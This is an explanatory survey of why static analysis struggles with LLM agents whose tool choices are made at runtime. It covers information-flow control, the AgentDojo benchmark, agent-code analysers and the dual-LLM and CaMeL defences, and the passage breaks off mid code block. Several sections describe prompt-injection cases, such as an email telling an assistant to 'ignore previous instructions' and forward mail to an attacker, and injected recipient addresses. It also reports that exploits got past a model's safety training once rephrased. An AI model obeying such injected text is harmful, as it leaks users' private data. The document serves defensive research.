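# Limits of static code analysis for systems where a model decides control flow at runtime

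## How a model's choices enter a program's control flow

Static code analysis examines a program's source code, without running it, to establish facts that hold for every possible run. Compilers use it to make programs faster, and security engineers use it to check, for example, whether untrusted text from a web form can reach a database command. It works because source code normally fixes a program's control flow, the order in which its operations run. Even if there are many branches and loops, an analyser can list them all from the code.

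In an agent built on a large language model (LLM), the model picks the next operation while the program is running, based on text that may come partly from strangers. The source code lists the available operations but doesn't fix their order. Researchers have been working out how much of existing program analysis still works for these agents. Some analyse the agent's source code anyway, some label data and check the labels during the run, and some have the model write a program first so that they can analyse it. All three approaches start from the same short loop.

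### The agent loop

Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*, adopt a definition by the programmer Simon Willison: an LLM agent "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal". A tool here is an ordinary function that the developer lets the model request, such as one that reads a mailbox. Without error handling, the loop looks like this:

```
messages = [system_prompt, user_request]
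for step in range(MAX_STEPS):
    reply = model(messages)
    messages.append(reply)
    if not reply.is_tool_call: return reply.text
    result = tools[reply.tool_name](**reply.arguments)
    messages.append(result)
```

The model produces only text. When the text has the right structure, the program parses it as a request to call a named tool with certain arguments, makes the call, adds the result to the conversation and queries the model again. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, stress that the program, not the model, is responsible for executing or refusing the request. The program can therefore check each request before making the call.

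The agent acts on the outside world only through the sixth line, which is identical in an agent that books flights and one that deletes files. Someone reading the source can see which functions are in the table `tools`, but not which of them will run, in what order or with what arguments. Many agents can also load "skills", which are text descriptions of how to do something, but the same skill can lead to different tool calls depending on the surrounding context, the model and the task. Pirch and colleagues call it a common misconception that a skill specifies a precise workflow.

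### What static analysis promises

A small function shows what an analyser does with code whose control flow is fixed. Kinder, in *Towards Static Analysis of Virtualization-Obfuscated Binaries*, published in 2012, uses one much like this:

```
def foo(x):
    y = 10
    y += 1
    y += 1
    if x > 0:
        y += 1
    call_api(y)
```

The analyser keeps a range of possible values for each variable and updates it line by line, without trying out values of `x`. After the two increments, `y` is 12. One branch makes it 13 and the other leaves it unchanged, so where the branches meet, the analyser merges the two results and records that `y` lies between 12 and 13, which holds for every possible `x`.

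Merging of this kind is over-approximation, meaning that the analyser treats every behaviour the code permits as possible, often including some that never occur. An analysis is sound if it never misses a violation of the property it checks. Soundness achieved through over-approximation can bring many false alarms, and even an analyser that reports a possible violation in every program is sound. Testing can miss violations because it covers only the runs that somebody tried. A dynamic check, which the program makes on actual values during a run, gives a definite answer about that run only.

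For programs with many functions, the analyser first needs a call graph, which has a node for each function and an edge wherever one function may call another. Ideally, the graph includes every call that could happen in any execution. Rafieian, Hicks and Wei (2026) report in *Agentic Root Cause Reasoning and Localization of Unsoundness in Static Call Graph* that this is rarely achievable in practice. A missing edge can cause errors in analyses that use the graph, such as taint tracking, which marks data by its source and carries the mark to whatever the program computes from it. Taint tracking aims to catch marked data on its way from a source, where untrusted or sensitive data enters, to a sink, an operation that such data must not reach unchecked. If the graph lacks the call through which the data travels, the analyser wrongly reports that the program is clean. If it lacks the call to the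 function that validates the data, the analyser raises a false alarm.

### Older ways of choosing a call at run time

Programs were choosing their next call at run time long before LLMs existed. The mildest case is dynamic dispatch in object-oriented languages, where `shape.area()` runs different code depending on whether `shape` holds a circle or a square. Analysers compute the set of objects the variable could hold and add a call-graph edge for each. *Control-Flow Integrity* (2016) explains that this step must be sound because compilers depend on it, and that it therefore over-approximates. When only one object is possible, the compiler can replace the run-time lookup with a direct call.

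Reflection is harder, because the program looks up a class or method by a name held in a string. Rafieian and colleagues give a Java example in which one line stores the word "Target" in a variable and the next line loads the class of that name. OPAL, a widely used analysis framework, resolves only literal strings in the part of its code that handles this step, so it omits the later call to `Target.hello()` and issues no warning. Rafieian and colleagues compared the static call graphs of OPAL and two similar tools with recordings of real runs, and found 1,459 calls that were missing from the graphs because of reflection and other causes. *Understanding and Analyzing Java Reflection* (2017) notes that analysing the strings helps only when their values can be known, and in many programs they cannot.

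Many scripting languages have an `eval` feature that runs a string as code, which changes the control-flow graph during the run. *SEA* (2017), which proposes an analysis for such strings, describes restricting or banning the feature as the usual response.

Mechanically, the agent's sixth line is reflection, because it looks up a function by a string, and no analyser can work out the string. An analyser can instead assume that the string could name any available function. In a large Java program, that assumption would add so many false edges that the call graph would be of little use, but an agent's tool table may have only half a dozen entries. An analyser that can find the table can draw one edge to each tool and have a sound call graph of the loop. The set of possible callees is then about as manageable as in dynamic dispatch. The order of the calls is still as unconstrained as in `eval`,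 and if one of the tools is a command shell or a Python interpreter, the callees are unconstrained too.

### The loop as an interpreter

The agent loop most closely resembles an interpreter, a program that reads another program and carries it out. Kinder studied interpreters used to hide malware. Malware writers translate their code into bytecode for a made-up instruction set and ship it with an interpreter. An analyst then finds a loop around a switch statement, with one case for each kind of instruction.

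Kinder applied this translation to the small function above and ran the same range analysis on the result. After the first instruction, the analyser correctly finds that `y` is 10. When the loop returns to its top, the analyser has to merge the states from before and after that instruction, so the range for `y` becomes 0 to 10. The position in the bytecode also widens, from 0 to a range of 0 to 3 and then 0 to 5. Soon the analyser can no longer separate instructions from their operands, and it loses any useful bound on `y`, although the analysis remains sound. All the instructions of the hidden program run through the same few lines, so any result for those lines must hold for the whole hidden program at once, an effect Kinder calls domain flattening.

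An agent loop has the same structure as a bytecode interpreter, with the conversation in place of the bytecode. The list `messages` corresponds to the program, the model decodes the next instruction, and the tool table is the instruction set. Facts that an analyser derives from the loop must be true for every task anyone could give the agent, so few of them are interesting.

Static analysis can still handle some interpreters. In 2012, Kinder kept a separate result for each position in the bytecode, which worked on a toy example. *Pushan* (Sudhir, Basque and colleagues, 2026) built on the idea and decompiled 988 of 1,000 test programs that one such obfuscator had produced; the best earlier tool recovered the complete control flow of 68. But this approach needs the bytecode, which those programs contain in the file. An agent's equivalent arrives during the run, first as the user's request and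 then as the emails, web pages and documents that the tools return. *Eventually Sound Points-To Analysis with Missing Code* (2017) points out that static analyses that promise soundness often assume that all of a program's source code is available. An agent's complete source code can still omit most of what determines its behaviour. Even if the text were available, the decoding step is a model rather than a switch statement with five cases, and the model's reply to the same conversation may vary from one call to the next.

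A static analyser examining an agent loop lacks an input, because nobody has written the emails the agent will read. The analyser has only the loop to work from, and this would be true even if it could escape Rice's theorem, the best-known limit on program analysis. The theorem holds that no algorithm can decide, for every possible program, any non-trivial property of what the program computes. It applies to payroll software as much as to agents, and analysers deal with it by over-approximating.

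### An assistant with six tools

Costa and colleagues describe an office assistant whose user asks it to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One of the emails includes a command to ignore previous instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to an attacker's address. If the model complies, the attacker has carried out a prompt injection, in which data that the agent was only meant to read "is obeyed as an instruction" (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026, *The LLMbda Calculus*). *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) attributes this weakness to LLMs operating directly on text, with no formal way to separate instructions from data. Pirch and colleagues found that all four of the popular open-source agents they examined put trusted and untrusted data into one shared context.

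Suppose the assistant has three tools that read (`read_email`, `read_calendar`, `read_file`) and three that act (`send_email`, `create_event`, `share_file`), and its loop stops after eight steps. The code then permits 6^8 = 1,679,616 different sequences of eight calls, not counting the possible arguments. Static analysis cannot determine which sequence will occur. *AGENTFLOW* (Wang, Hou and colleagues, 2026), a static analyser for agent programs, therefore over-approximates the behaviour that the program's structure permits.

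The analyser can also check whether outside text can influence an action. The loop appends every tool result to the conversation and passes the whole conversation to the model, so the analyser has to assume that anything a reading tool returns may affect any later call. With three reading tools and three acting tools, there are nine pairs in which a reading tool is followed by an acting tool, and a sound analysis with no further information flags all nine. The honest run needs only one of them, `read_email` followed by `send_email`. The analysis also flags most whole runs. Only 59,049 sequences, or 3.5%, contain no flagged pair, and these are the ones that make all their acting calls before any reading calls.

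A developer can limit what the assistant can do by giving it only the two email tools. If those tools' own code does nothing else, static analysis can guarantee that no run shares a file or creates a calendar event, whatever the emails contain. This restriction does not stop the attack, because the attack uses the same two tools that the legitimate task needs. The two runs differ in where the decision to send, the content and the address came from, and a call graph cannot record those origins.

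### Labels and their lattice

Information-flow control (IFC) gives each value a label, and rules on labels govern where the value may go and what it may influence. A confidentiality label specifies who may read the value, and an integrity label records who may have influenced it. The simplest form of IFC is taint tracking with a single "untrusted" mark.

The mathematics comes from Denning's 1976 paper, *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*. Denning orders the labels by a relation "may flow to", so that public data may flow into a secret file but not the reverse. Any two labels must also have a join, which is the least restrictive label that both may flow to. Labels with this structure form a lattice. When a program computes a value from several inputs, the value's label is the join of the inputs' labels. The program may store the value in a location only if the value's label may flow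 to the location's label.

Costa and colleagues work out the join of two documents' labels. People A, B and C may read the first document, and B, C and D may read the second. Text derived from both may go only to people who are allowed to read both, so its label is the intersection, {B, C}. If the same two sets instead list who could have written to each document, the join is the union, {A, B, C, D}, because any of the four could have contributed to the combined text. Combining documents can therefore reduce the number of permitted readers and increase the number of possible writers. Many systems use only two values for each kind of label, public or secret and trusted or untrusted, which makes four combined labels. These form a lattice with trusted public data, which may flow anywhere, at the bottom and untrusted secret data at the top.

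If labels are applied naively to the agent loop, every tool request becomes untrusted after the assistant has read one outside email. The model's reply may depend on anything in the conversation, so without further knowledge its label has to be the join of the labels of all the messages. A rule that allows `send_email` only on a trusted request stops the attack, but it also blocks the summary for the manager. Sabelfeld and Myers (2003), in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security*, call this effect label creep and say that it makes systems that compute labels at run time too restrictive to be generally useful. Agent designers who want to use labels need a way to avoid it.

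### Explicit and implicit flows

Data can also get out without anyone copying it. An explicit flow copies data or computes with it, as in `b = a + 1`. An implicit flow reveals data through the choice of a branch. Sabelfeld and Myers give an example that comes to this:

```
low = 0
if secret % 2 == 1:
    low = 1
```

After the program runs, `low` holds the last binary digit of `secret`, even though no line copies `secret` into `low`. A monitor that checks assignments as they happen can catch the case where `secret` is odd, because the program then assigns to a public variable under a secret condition. When `secret` is even, the assignment never runs, so the monitor has nothing to check, but anyone who reads the 0 in `low` still learns the digit. A compiler does better because it can examine the branch that a given run skips. Sabelfeld and Myers conclude more generally that confidentiality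 is a property of the set of all possible executions, so watching a single one cannot establish it.

Static analysis can examine both branches of a condition, which is perhaps the strongest classical argument for it, but the agent loop weakens that argument. An agent branches when its model chooses a tool. Garby and colleagues imagine an injected instruction that makes an agent send the fixed text "rich!" to an outsider if an account balance exceeds some threshold. The text contains nothing secret, but its arrival reveals that the balance is above the threshold. If the model writes that condition as code, an analyser can examine both branches, but if the model makes the decision itself, the source contains no `if` statement to examine, only the sixth line of the loop.

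### Noninterference and its exceptions

Noninterference is the standard way to state that nothing leaks by either kind of flow. It means that changing the protected inputs changes nothing that an observer at a given level can see. A program P that takes a secret input h and a public input l is noninterfering if, for every l and every pair of secrets h1 and h2, P(h1, l) and P(h2, l) produce the same public outputs. Since a model's replies are partly random, Garby and colleagues state the property for agents in terms of probabilities. The corresponding property for integrity is that changing the untrusted inputs changes nothing that is supposed to be trusted.

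The assistant cannot satisfy noninterference and still summarize outside emails for the manager. If the emails are untrusted and the message to the manager has to be trusted, noninterference requires the same message whatever the emails say. Costa and colleagues similarly conclude that, for confidentiality, full noninterference would in effect forbid any call that may write to a public place after any call that may have read something secret. Their system, FIDES, settles for a weaker property, explicit secrecy, which does not cover implicit flows.

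The difficulty long predates agents, and real systems deal with it by allowing exceptions. *Attacker Control and Impact for Confidentiality and Integrity* (Askarov and Myers, 2011) distinguishes two kinds. Declassification deliberately relabels secret data as public or, more generally, opens it to more readers, as when a user has private mail summarised for a manager who could not read the originals. Endorsement deliberately relabels untrusted data as trusted, as when a program accepts a meeting date from an outside email after checking that it is a date.

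Each exception weakens the guarantee, and an attacker might be able to widen it. Robust declassification requires that an attacker who corrupts data cannot make the program release additional or different secrets. The injected email is an attempt to do this, by making the program release the top message in the mailbox instead of a summary. *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real–Ideal Paradigm* (2026) informally describes transparent endorsement as allowing a program to endorse a value only if whoever supplied the value could already read it. Without that condition, according to *Nonmalleable Information Flow* (2017), the supplier could affect how the endorser's own secrets flow into trusted data.

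### How AgentDojo tests an agent

Most of the designs that apply these ideas to agents report results on one benchmark, AgentDojo, which Debenedetti and colleagues released in 2024. It simulates four environments, each with its own tools and made-up data: an office workspace with 40 user tasks, the messaging service Slack with 21, a travel agency with 20 and a bank with 16, or 97 in all. A typical task is to pay a bill that the user has stored as a text file. Each environment also has five to nine injection tasks, which are goals for an attacker, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker's account. The benchmark pairs every user task with every injection task in the same environment, which gives 16 × 9 = 144 pairs for the bank and 629 across all four environments. Later work uses a larger version, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026)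 counts over 900 pairs.

In an attacked run, the attacker's text appears where an outsider could plausibly have put it, such as the body of an email the agent has to read. Ordinary code then checks the state of the environment to determine whether the money moved or the email went out. Debenedetti and colleagues did not use a second model as the judge because a successful injection might hijack it as well. They also designed the benchmark so that others could add attacks, reasoning that it is extremely easy to build a defence that stops one specific attack but fails against an attacker who adapts to it.

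The benchmark yields three scores. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when nobody attacks it. Utility under attack is the share of pairs in which the agent completes the user's task without harmful side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share of pairs in which the attacker achieves their goal.

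## Static analysers that read agent source code

Developers commonly take the agent loop from a framework such as LangGraph, CrewAI or the OpenAI Agents SDK. Their own code declares the agents and the tools each one has. The framework looks up tools by name, so the developer's code may never call `send_email` itself. To connect the loop to its tools, an analyser needs information about how each framework uses those declarations. AgentFlow, which Wang and colleagues presented in July 2026, has this information built in.

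### A graph of declarations

The following program, simplified from the one that Wang and colleagues use, has two agents:

```
send_email = RemoteTool(MAIL_SERVER, require_approval="always")
ops = Agent(tools=[send_email])
research = Agent(tools=[web_search], handoffs=[ops])
run(research, user_request, session=shared_memory)
```

The user asks for recent news on a subject and wants it emailed to a colleague. The research agent can search the web but cannot send mail, so it has to hand the task to the operations agent. The mail tool runs on a remote server, which the program reaches through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to outside tools. A person must approve every email.

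AgentFlow turns a program like this into a graph with six kinds of node: agents, prompts, models, capabilities (tools, MCP servers and skills), memory, and control policies such as the approval rule. Component edges attach each agent to its prompt, model, tools and memory. Control edges lead from an agent to any tool or agent that may run next, and if a policy guards that step, the edge passes through the policy's node. Data edges show where information may travel: from prompts into agents, from agents into tool arguments, from tool results back into agents, between agents, and in and out of memory. For the program above, the main control and data edges are these:

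```
control:  research -> web_search
          research -> ops
          ops -> approval -> send_email

data:     user_request -> research -> ops -> send_email
          web_search -> research
          research -> shared_memory -> ops
```

To build the graph, AgentFlow first looks for the constructs it models, such as the `Agent(...)` constructor or the marker that registers a function as a tool. It models 143 constructs across five frameworks, counting LangChain and LangGraph as one. It then resolves names, linking `send_email` in the operations agent's tool list to the line that defines the tool and its approval setting. It records each resolved construct as a short fact, for example that `research` may transfer control to `ops`. From these facts, it draws the edges inside each agent and then those between agents.

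The edge from `research` to `ops` means only that the program gives the model the option of a handoff.

### Running the prompt-to-tool query

Once the graph exists, a security check is a search through it. Wang and colleagues look for cases where a prompt can influence what an agent passes to a sensitive tool. Their query reports a prompt p, an agent a and a tool c if all of the following hold:

1. A path of data edges leads from p to a.
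2. A path of control edges leads from a to c.
3. A data edge carries arguments directly from a to c.

Suppose the user's request is the only prompt of interest and `send_email` is the only sensitive tool. The request reaches the operations agent, `ops`, through the research agent's handoff message and through the shared memory. A control path leads from `ops` to `send_email`, and `ops` fills in the tool's arguments, so the query reports the request, `ops` and `send_email`. It doesn't report the research agent, although data reaches that agent and control can pass from it to `send_email` through `ops`, because the query requires a direct argument edge and the research agent never writes the email's arguments itself.

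The approval rule doesn't change the result. A control path through the approval node still counts as a path, because no condition exempts guarded steps. This seems right for a search meant to miss little, since people do approve things they shouldn't. But a developer who already requires a person to approve every email gets the same report as one who doesn't, and has to look at the graph to see the difference.

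The query also starts from prompts, but a prompt injection would more likely arrive in a web page. The graph includes an edge from `web_search` back to the research agent, so a query starting at `web_search` would follow the same route to the mail tool.

### What AgentFlow found in 5,399 programs

Wang and colleagues collected 5,399 Python projects from GitHub, about 70% of them built with LangChain or LangGraph, and ran the query on all of them. It flagged 238 projects (4.4%), with 4,357 findings in total, or about 18 per flagged project. In 129 of the flagged projects, the tool at the end of the path could send something to the outside world. Such tools could access files in 74 projects, query databases in 42, and run commands or code in 41. Some projects fell into more than one group.

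The 238 are projects with at least one AgentFlow report, and nobody checked them all, though the abstract describes them as risks that AgentFlow uncovered. Two of the researchers read the source code behind a sample of 100 reports and judged 73 to be real vulnerabilities, a precision (the share of reports that are right) of 73%. Of the 27 false alarms, 25 contained a valid path from prompt to tool, but the reviewers rejected them because the tool seemed harmless: 13 only read local files, 7 ran read-only database queries and 5 were restricted calculators.

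AgentFlow traced the path correctly in at least 98 of the 100 cases, and nearly all of its errors concerned what the tool at the end of the path could do. Some of those errors are debatable. Reading a local file does no damage by itself, but an agent that can also send the contents somewhere could leak them.

The same two reviewers looked at 100 agents that had powerful tools but no report, and found nine risks that AgentFlow had missed. The causes included custom command wrappers, dynamically attached tools and the developers' own orchestration code. This sample alone doesn't give the share of all risks that AgentFlow misses, because that share also depends on how many agents with powerful tools have no report. Both audits relied on reading code, so a report counted as "real" if the path existed and ended somewhere dangerous, even if nobody had successfully attacked the agent.

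### Inventories of agent components

AgentFlow produces an agent bill of materials by collecting everything that component edges connect to each agent. An ordinary bill of materials lists the packages inside a software product, and companies often keep one so that they can tell whether a newly discovered flaw affects them. The agent version adds the agents, prompts, models, tools and memory, and records which belongs to which.

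Wang and colleagues compared AgentFlow's inventory with those of three existing tools on a sample of 100 projects. AgentFlow listed 2,295 components and 1,008 connections between them, while Cisco's tool listed 141 components and 22 connections. Trusera's tool produced the longest list, with 3,615 entries, but these were mostly models and software packages and included no agents or tools. The counts show what each tool tries to cover more than how well it does so, since a longer list is better only if its entries are correct.

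A developer can use an inventory to plan which tools each agent gets. For example, the developer can withhold tools that take actions from an agent that reads untrusted pages and from every agent it can hand over to.

### Inside the tools

AgentFlow treats each tool as a single node and does not examine the code inside. Much of the danger is in that code, as three versions of the same tool make clear:

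```
def tool_a(cmd):
    run_shell(cmd)

def tool_b(cmd):
    cmd = "date"
    run_shell(cmd)

def tool_c(cmd):
    if cmd in ALLOWED:
        run_shell(cmd)
```

The tools `tool_a`, `tool_b` and `tool_c` all run a shell command. In `tool_a` the model chooses the command freely, in `tool_b` its choice has no effect, and in `tool_c` it can choose only from a list. *Beyond Predefined Sinks* (Cui, 2026) uses three similar tools to argue that finding a dangerous operation is only a starting point. Cui's analyser, AgentSecGraph, collects evidence about whether an agent can reach each such operation, which inputs may affect it, and whether it has anything resembling a guard.

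AgentSecGraph found 23,866 sensitive operations in 67 agent repositories. It could trace an input to 41% of them and found a possible guard on 13%. Cui does not call any of these vulnerabilities. Separately, Cui reproduced 22 sensitive behaviours under controlled conditions. One was a confirmed vulnerability and one was awaiting disclosure. The other 20 did not qualify as vulnerabilities because of protections or limits on use. AgentSecGraph can identify a possible guard, but it cannot determine whether the guard is good enough.

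*TaintP2X* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) checks only whether text that a model generates can flow into a dangerous operation in ordinary application code. It reports such paths across 75 open-source repositories. Developers confirmed seven vulnerabilities and fixed five. Seven is a small number, but confirmation by maintainers is stronger evidence than a researcher's reading of the code. Wang and colleagues point out that TaintP2X does not directly handle programs whose structure comes from an agent framework, so the two analysers cover different kinds of program.

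Some flaws can be found without reasoning about the model. *Agent Audit* (2026) describes a scanner that follows data through tool functions and reads deployment files, looking for exposed passwords and for MCP configurations that grant too many privileges. It found 40 of 42 known vulnerabilities in 22 samples, with six false alarms, and each scan took less than a second. The scanner may perform less well on real projects. *AgentLens* (2026) reports that it yielded no validated vulnerabilities in Langflow, an open-source platform for building agents, and notes more generally that a flaw flagged by static analysis may not be triggerable in an actual run.

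### Tools that are dangerous together

A program can leak data even when each of its functions looks harmless on its own. *ACaM* (Santra, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a news tool that stores its access token in a dictionary shared with other tools. A second tool synchronises the user's preferences by posting that whole dictionary to another server. If the model calls the news tool and then the preferences tool, the second call sends the token to a server that doesn't need it. The model chooses tools using only their descriptions, and neither description mentions this.

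ACaM ignores tool descriptions and works out from the code what each tool can do. It checks 19 standard properties, such as whether a tool reads a secret or starts another process, and adds others for each agent. Static analysis settles as many as it can, and a language model fills in those that depend on what the code means. For example, a branch on `user.role` probably controls privileges, while one on `user.lang` probably doesn't. The model's answers cannot override what static analysis has established.

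In the news example, ACaM first records that the preferences tool leaks a secret if another tool writes one into the shared dictionary. It then combines the results for all the tools, finds that the news tool writes a secret there, and changes the conditional result to a positive one. ACaM assumes the worst case for the order of calls.

Santra and colleagues tested this on 14 agents in which they had planted leaks, scoring how much of each chain an analyser reconstructed. ACaM scored 0.98 out of 1, and the best results from language models working without static analysis averaged 0.90. Pysa, a conventional taint tracker, scored 0.34. When the researchers told Pysa to treat the model call as a function that passes taint from input to output, which is the obvious way to adapt such a tool, its score fell to 0.23. They attribute the drop to noise that the analysis could not resolve. (How much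 an input really affects a model's output is a question for separate estimators.)

The researchers also ran ACaM on 43 unmodified agents. It found 123 critical paths, which allowed code execution or exposed credentials, and they confirmed by hand that each existed in the code. They built working exploits for ten findings of critical or high severity. These exploits are better evidence than an audit of source code, but ten are too few to show much about the roughly 1,800 other paths.

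*AgentRaft* (2026) describes a system that uses static analysis to narrow down which combinations of tools to test. The system builds a graph with an edge between two tools wherever data from one could plausibly serve the other, and a language model checks the candidate pairs. It then uses the graph to write prompts that test for data over-exposure, where an agent passes on more data than the task needs.

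### The code around the model

Some agents are complete programs that people install on their own computers. OpenClaw, a popular one, can run shell commands, read files, control a browser and use stored passwords. A lot of ordinary code between the model and the machine builds prompts, parses replies, loads skills and checks permissions. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) studies how well static analysis finds flaws in this code.

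Researchers gathered 446 public security advisories for OpenClaw, along with the code from before each fix, and ran two widely used analysers on that code. Semgrep matches patterns in a program's syntax, and CodeQL queries a database of its structure. On the 217 most recent advisories, Semgrep found 21.7% of the flaws and CodeQL found 13.8%. On the 229 older ones, Semgrep found 25.3% and CodeQL found 12.2%.

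Zhang and colleagues then wrote 47 rules for Semgrep and 30 queries for CodeQL, using only the older advisories. On the recent advisories, recall (the share of known flaws found) rose to 66.8% for Semgrep and 75.1% for CodeQL. Symbolic links are file names that point to other files, and they can lead a program out of the folder it is supposed to stay in. Semgrep had found none of the 15 symbolic-link flaws in the whole set, but it found 13 with the new rules. The standard rules cover web application operations, such as a web request flowing into a database command, and an agent's prompt builder or skill loader doesn't resemble those.

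The scoring was generous because an analyser received credit for a flaw if it flagged anything in a file that the fix later changed, even an unrelated line. A rule set that raises more alarms will therefore tend to score higher. With the new rules, the two analysers produced 3,473 and 3,756 findings on the then current version of OpenClaw, which had 16,433 source files. The researchers checked 25 findings from each analyser and judged three in each sample to be correct, a precision of 12%. All six came from narrow rules aimed at a specific mistake.

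Certain flaws have no recognisable form in code. If a program blocks a list of dangerous commands and the list is missing one, the code looks the same as it would with a complete list. An analyser can't detect the gap unless somebody supplies the full list. Even with the new rules, Semgrep found only 37.5% of these flaws and CodeQL 50%.

### Whether a loop has a bound

The basic agent loop stops after at most `MAX_STEPS` steps, whatever the model outputs. If a developer replaces the `for` line with `while True`, the run may end only when the model stops calling tools. *When Agents Do Not Stop* (Hou, Wang and colleagues, 2026) calls the resulting failure an infinite agentic loop. It can run up a large bill, fill the model's context window or repeat an action with outside effects.

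The analyser IAL-Scan builds a graph of the program and looks for cycles that repeatedly call a model or tool, or keep adding to the conversation. For each cycle, it works out what decides whether to continue and whether an effective bound applies. A test of the model's own output doesn't count as a bound, nor does a limit on an inner loop if an outer loop can keep restarting it.

An assistant published by NVIDIA calls the model inside a `while True` loop. If the reply is empty, the program adds a message asking for a real answer and tries again, with no limit on retries, so each failure makes the conversation longer. The loop works as long as the model eventually returns a non-empty reply, which is probably why nobody noticed the missing limit.

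IAL-Scan flagged 74 loops as unbounded across 6,549 repositories, and manual review confirmed 68 of them in 47 projects. The other six had bounds that were hard to find, such as a framework's default limit of three iterations. A general coding agent given the same task on 264 of the projects found 50 of the 68 confirmed loops and timed out or hit an error in 75 projects.

Static analysis suits this property because a step counter works the same way whatever the model outputs. Merging states made the analyser lose the useful facts in Kinder's interpreter, but it does no harm here because the relevant fact is the same on every pass and for every task. If an analyser correctly finds a hard limit on the number of steps, that limit is guaranteed for all runs, including runs under attack. The guarantee doesn't cover what the agent does in those steps, so an agent limited to eight steps can still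 delete many files.

A developer learns less from a missing bound, because the program permits an endless run but the model may stop after two steps every time. The reviewers confirmed the 68 cases by reading code, not by observing large bills from actual runs.

IAL-Scan does not provide a proof either. Its static stage produced the same 340 candidates on each of three runs, and a language model then discarded those that looked harmless. This filtering was less consistent, and the three runs ended with 68, 64 and 60 of the confirmed loops. Hou and colleagues also checked what the coding agent and another model-based method had reported, and found seven loops that IAL-Scan had missed.

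### What a finding means and what a clean report leaves open

These analysers report paths that the program permits, but whether a run takes one depends on the model, the task and what the agent reads. Nine of Santra and colleagues' ten exploits worked on the first attempt with a small model that had little safety training. Claude Haiku 4.5, which has much more safety training, blocked the blunt versions, but all ten succeeded once the researchers phrased the attack more subtly. Two of the ten didn't depend on a model's decision, because the agent loaded a file in an unsafe format when it started, and anyone able to tamper with that file could run code.

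A report with no findings is harder to interpret. In the two-agent program, the code of `send_email` is on someone else's server. AgentFlow can detect that the tool exists and needs approval, but not what it does, and the server's owner can change it without any change to the developer's repository. If the program accepts whatever tools a server offers when it connects, the source doesn't even contain the tools' names. Code that the agent writes during a run is also missing from the source, and a type checker can examine it only once it exists.

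An analyser that doesn't recognise a framework may treat its agents and tools as ordinary function calls, then produce a small graph and report no problems. AgentFlow covers five frameworks, all in Python, and those change quickly. ACaM is better in one respect, because it marks constructs it cannot resolve as unknown instead of safe, so a developer can tell which parts of the code it was unable to check. But it excludes remote components and code that a program assembles at run time. It also gives an intermediate label to files whose paths the program computes at run time, although some may hold secrets, because labelling them all secret would flood the results.

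### Sound analysers and useful ones

None of these analysers is sound. AgentFlow over-approximates what the model may do with the constructs it recognises, so it reports paths that may never occur. It also misses some paths because it leaves out constructs it doesn't recognise. Cui says that AgentSecGraph's analysis is incomplete, and the others make similar compromises.

A sound analyser for agents would be easy to build but too imprecise to be useful. It could flag every pair of a reading tool and an acting tool, as in the office assistant, and assume that a remote server might offer any tool. It would then flag everything in any program with a remote server.

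An unsound analyser can be useful because it finds real mistakes quickly, while they are still easy to fix. AgentFlow takes a median of 14 seconds per program, so a developer can run it after every change. Many of the flaws these tools find are ordinary programming errors, such as an interpreter without a sandbox or a missing ownership check, and fixing them in the code works whichever model the agent uses. Santra and colleagues argue that removing such errors before deployment reduces what runtime defences must handle. They add that a model of what each tool can do would help in writing the labels or policies those defences need. This case for unsound analysers holds as long as most reports are correct, since at 12% precision a team would spend most of its time dismissing false ones.

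A bug finder helps much less when the path it reports is not a mistake. Of the roughly 1,900 paths that ACaM reported in the 43 agents, 1,692 were routes for indirect prompt injection, where outside text reaches the model through a tool. Santra and colleagues regard this exposure as inherent in the design, since prompts mix data with instructions. The developer of the office assistant cannot remove such a path by correcting a line, because the assistant's job is to read emails and send a summary. To close the path without removing a tool, the developer would have to redesign the agent so that the text of an email no longer influences which tool runs next.

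## The dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL

In the basic agent loop, the model that reads the emails also chooses the tools. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed giving these jobs to two models. The planner, which Willison calls the privileged LLM, takes the user's request and chooses tool calls, but never reads text that an outsider could have written. The quarantined model reads that text and has no tools. Willison advises developers to expect that the quarantined model could "go rogue at any moment".

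Ordinary software, called the controller, passes results between the two models. It stores each result in a variable and gives the planner only the variable's name. The planner can instruct the controller to send `$VAR2` to somebody without having access to the variable's contents.

A simpler safeguard would be to have the user approve every action. Willison expected that to fail, because people would soon learn to click "OK" on everything.

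### The office assistant with two models

Suppose the user again asks for a summary of recent emails about Project X, to go to a manager whose address the user supplies. The run has three steps:

1. The planner requests `read_email("Project X")`. The controller makes the call, stores the emails as `$VAR1` and gives the planner that name.
2. The planner requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller inserts the emails into a prompt for the quarantined model and stores the reply as `$VAR2`.
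3. The planner requests `send_email(manager, $VAR2)`. The controller fills in the summary and sends it.

The injected command to forward the top email reaches the quarantined model in the second step. Even if the model follows the command, it can only produce text, which is stored in `$VAR2`. The command never reaches the planner, so the third step stays the same. The attacker can still spoil the summary, for instance by making it empty or false, and the manager will receive it as if it were genuine.

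Willison allows one exception to the rule that the planner sees only names. If the quarantined model sorts an email into one of a few fixed categories, the controller can check that the reply is exactly one of them and then show it to the planner, because a reply that passes this check can't contain a new instruction.

The pattern assumes that the user's request is trustworthy. This assumption fails if someone tricks the user into pasting in an attacker's text. The assistant can also leak private data by displaying an image whose web address contains that data, because loading the image sends the address to the image's server. Willison called the proposal "pretty bad", mainly because it is complicated to build and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the planner would undo the protection.

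### When the address comes from an email

The pattern itself also has a gap. Suppose the user doesn't know the manager's address and tells the assistant to find it in the emails. The planner has the quarantined model extract the address into `$VAR3` and requests `send_email($VAR3, $VAR2)`. An injected instruction can make the quarantined model return the attacker's address instead. The assistant still makes exactly the calls the planner chose, but the summary goes to the attacker.

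Researchers at Google DeepMind pointed this out in 2025 when they presented CaMeL, a system that builds on the dual-LLM pattern. Willison (2025) accepted the criticism in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. In the researchers' example, a user wants to send Bob a document, and both Bob's address and the document's name are in a file of meeting notes.

### What CaMeL adds

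CaMeL's planner writes a complete program from the user's request before any tool runs. For the request without an address, the program might look like this:

```
emails = read_email("Project X")
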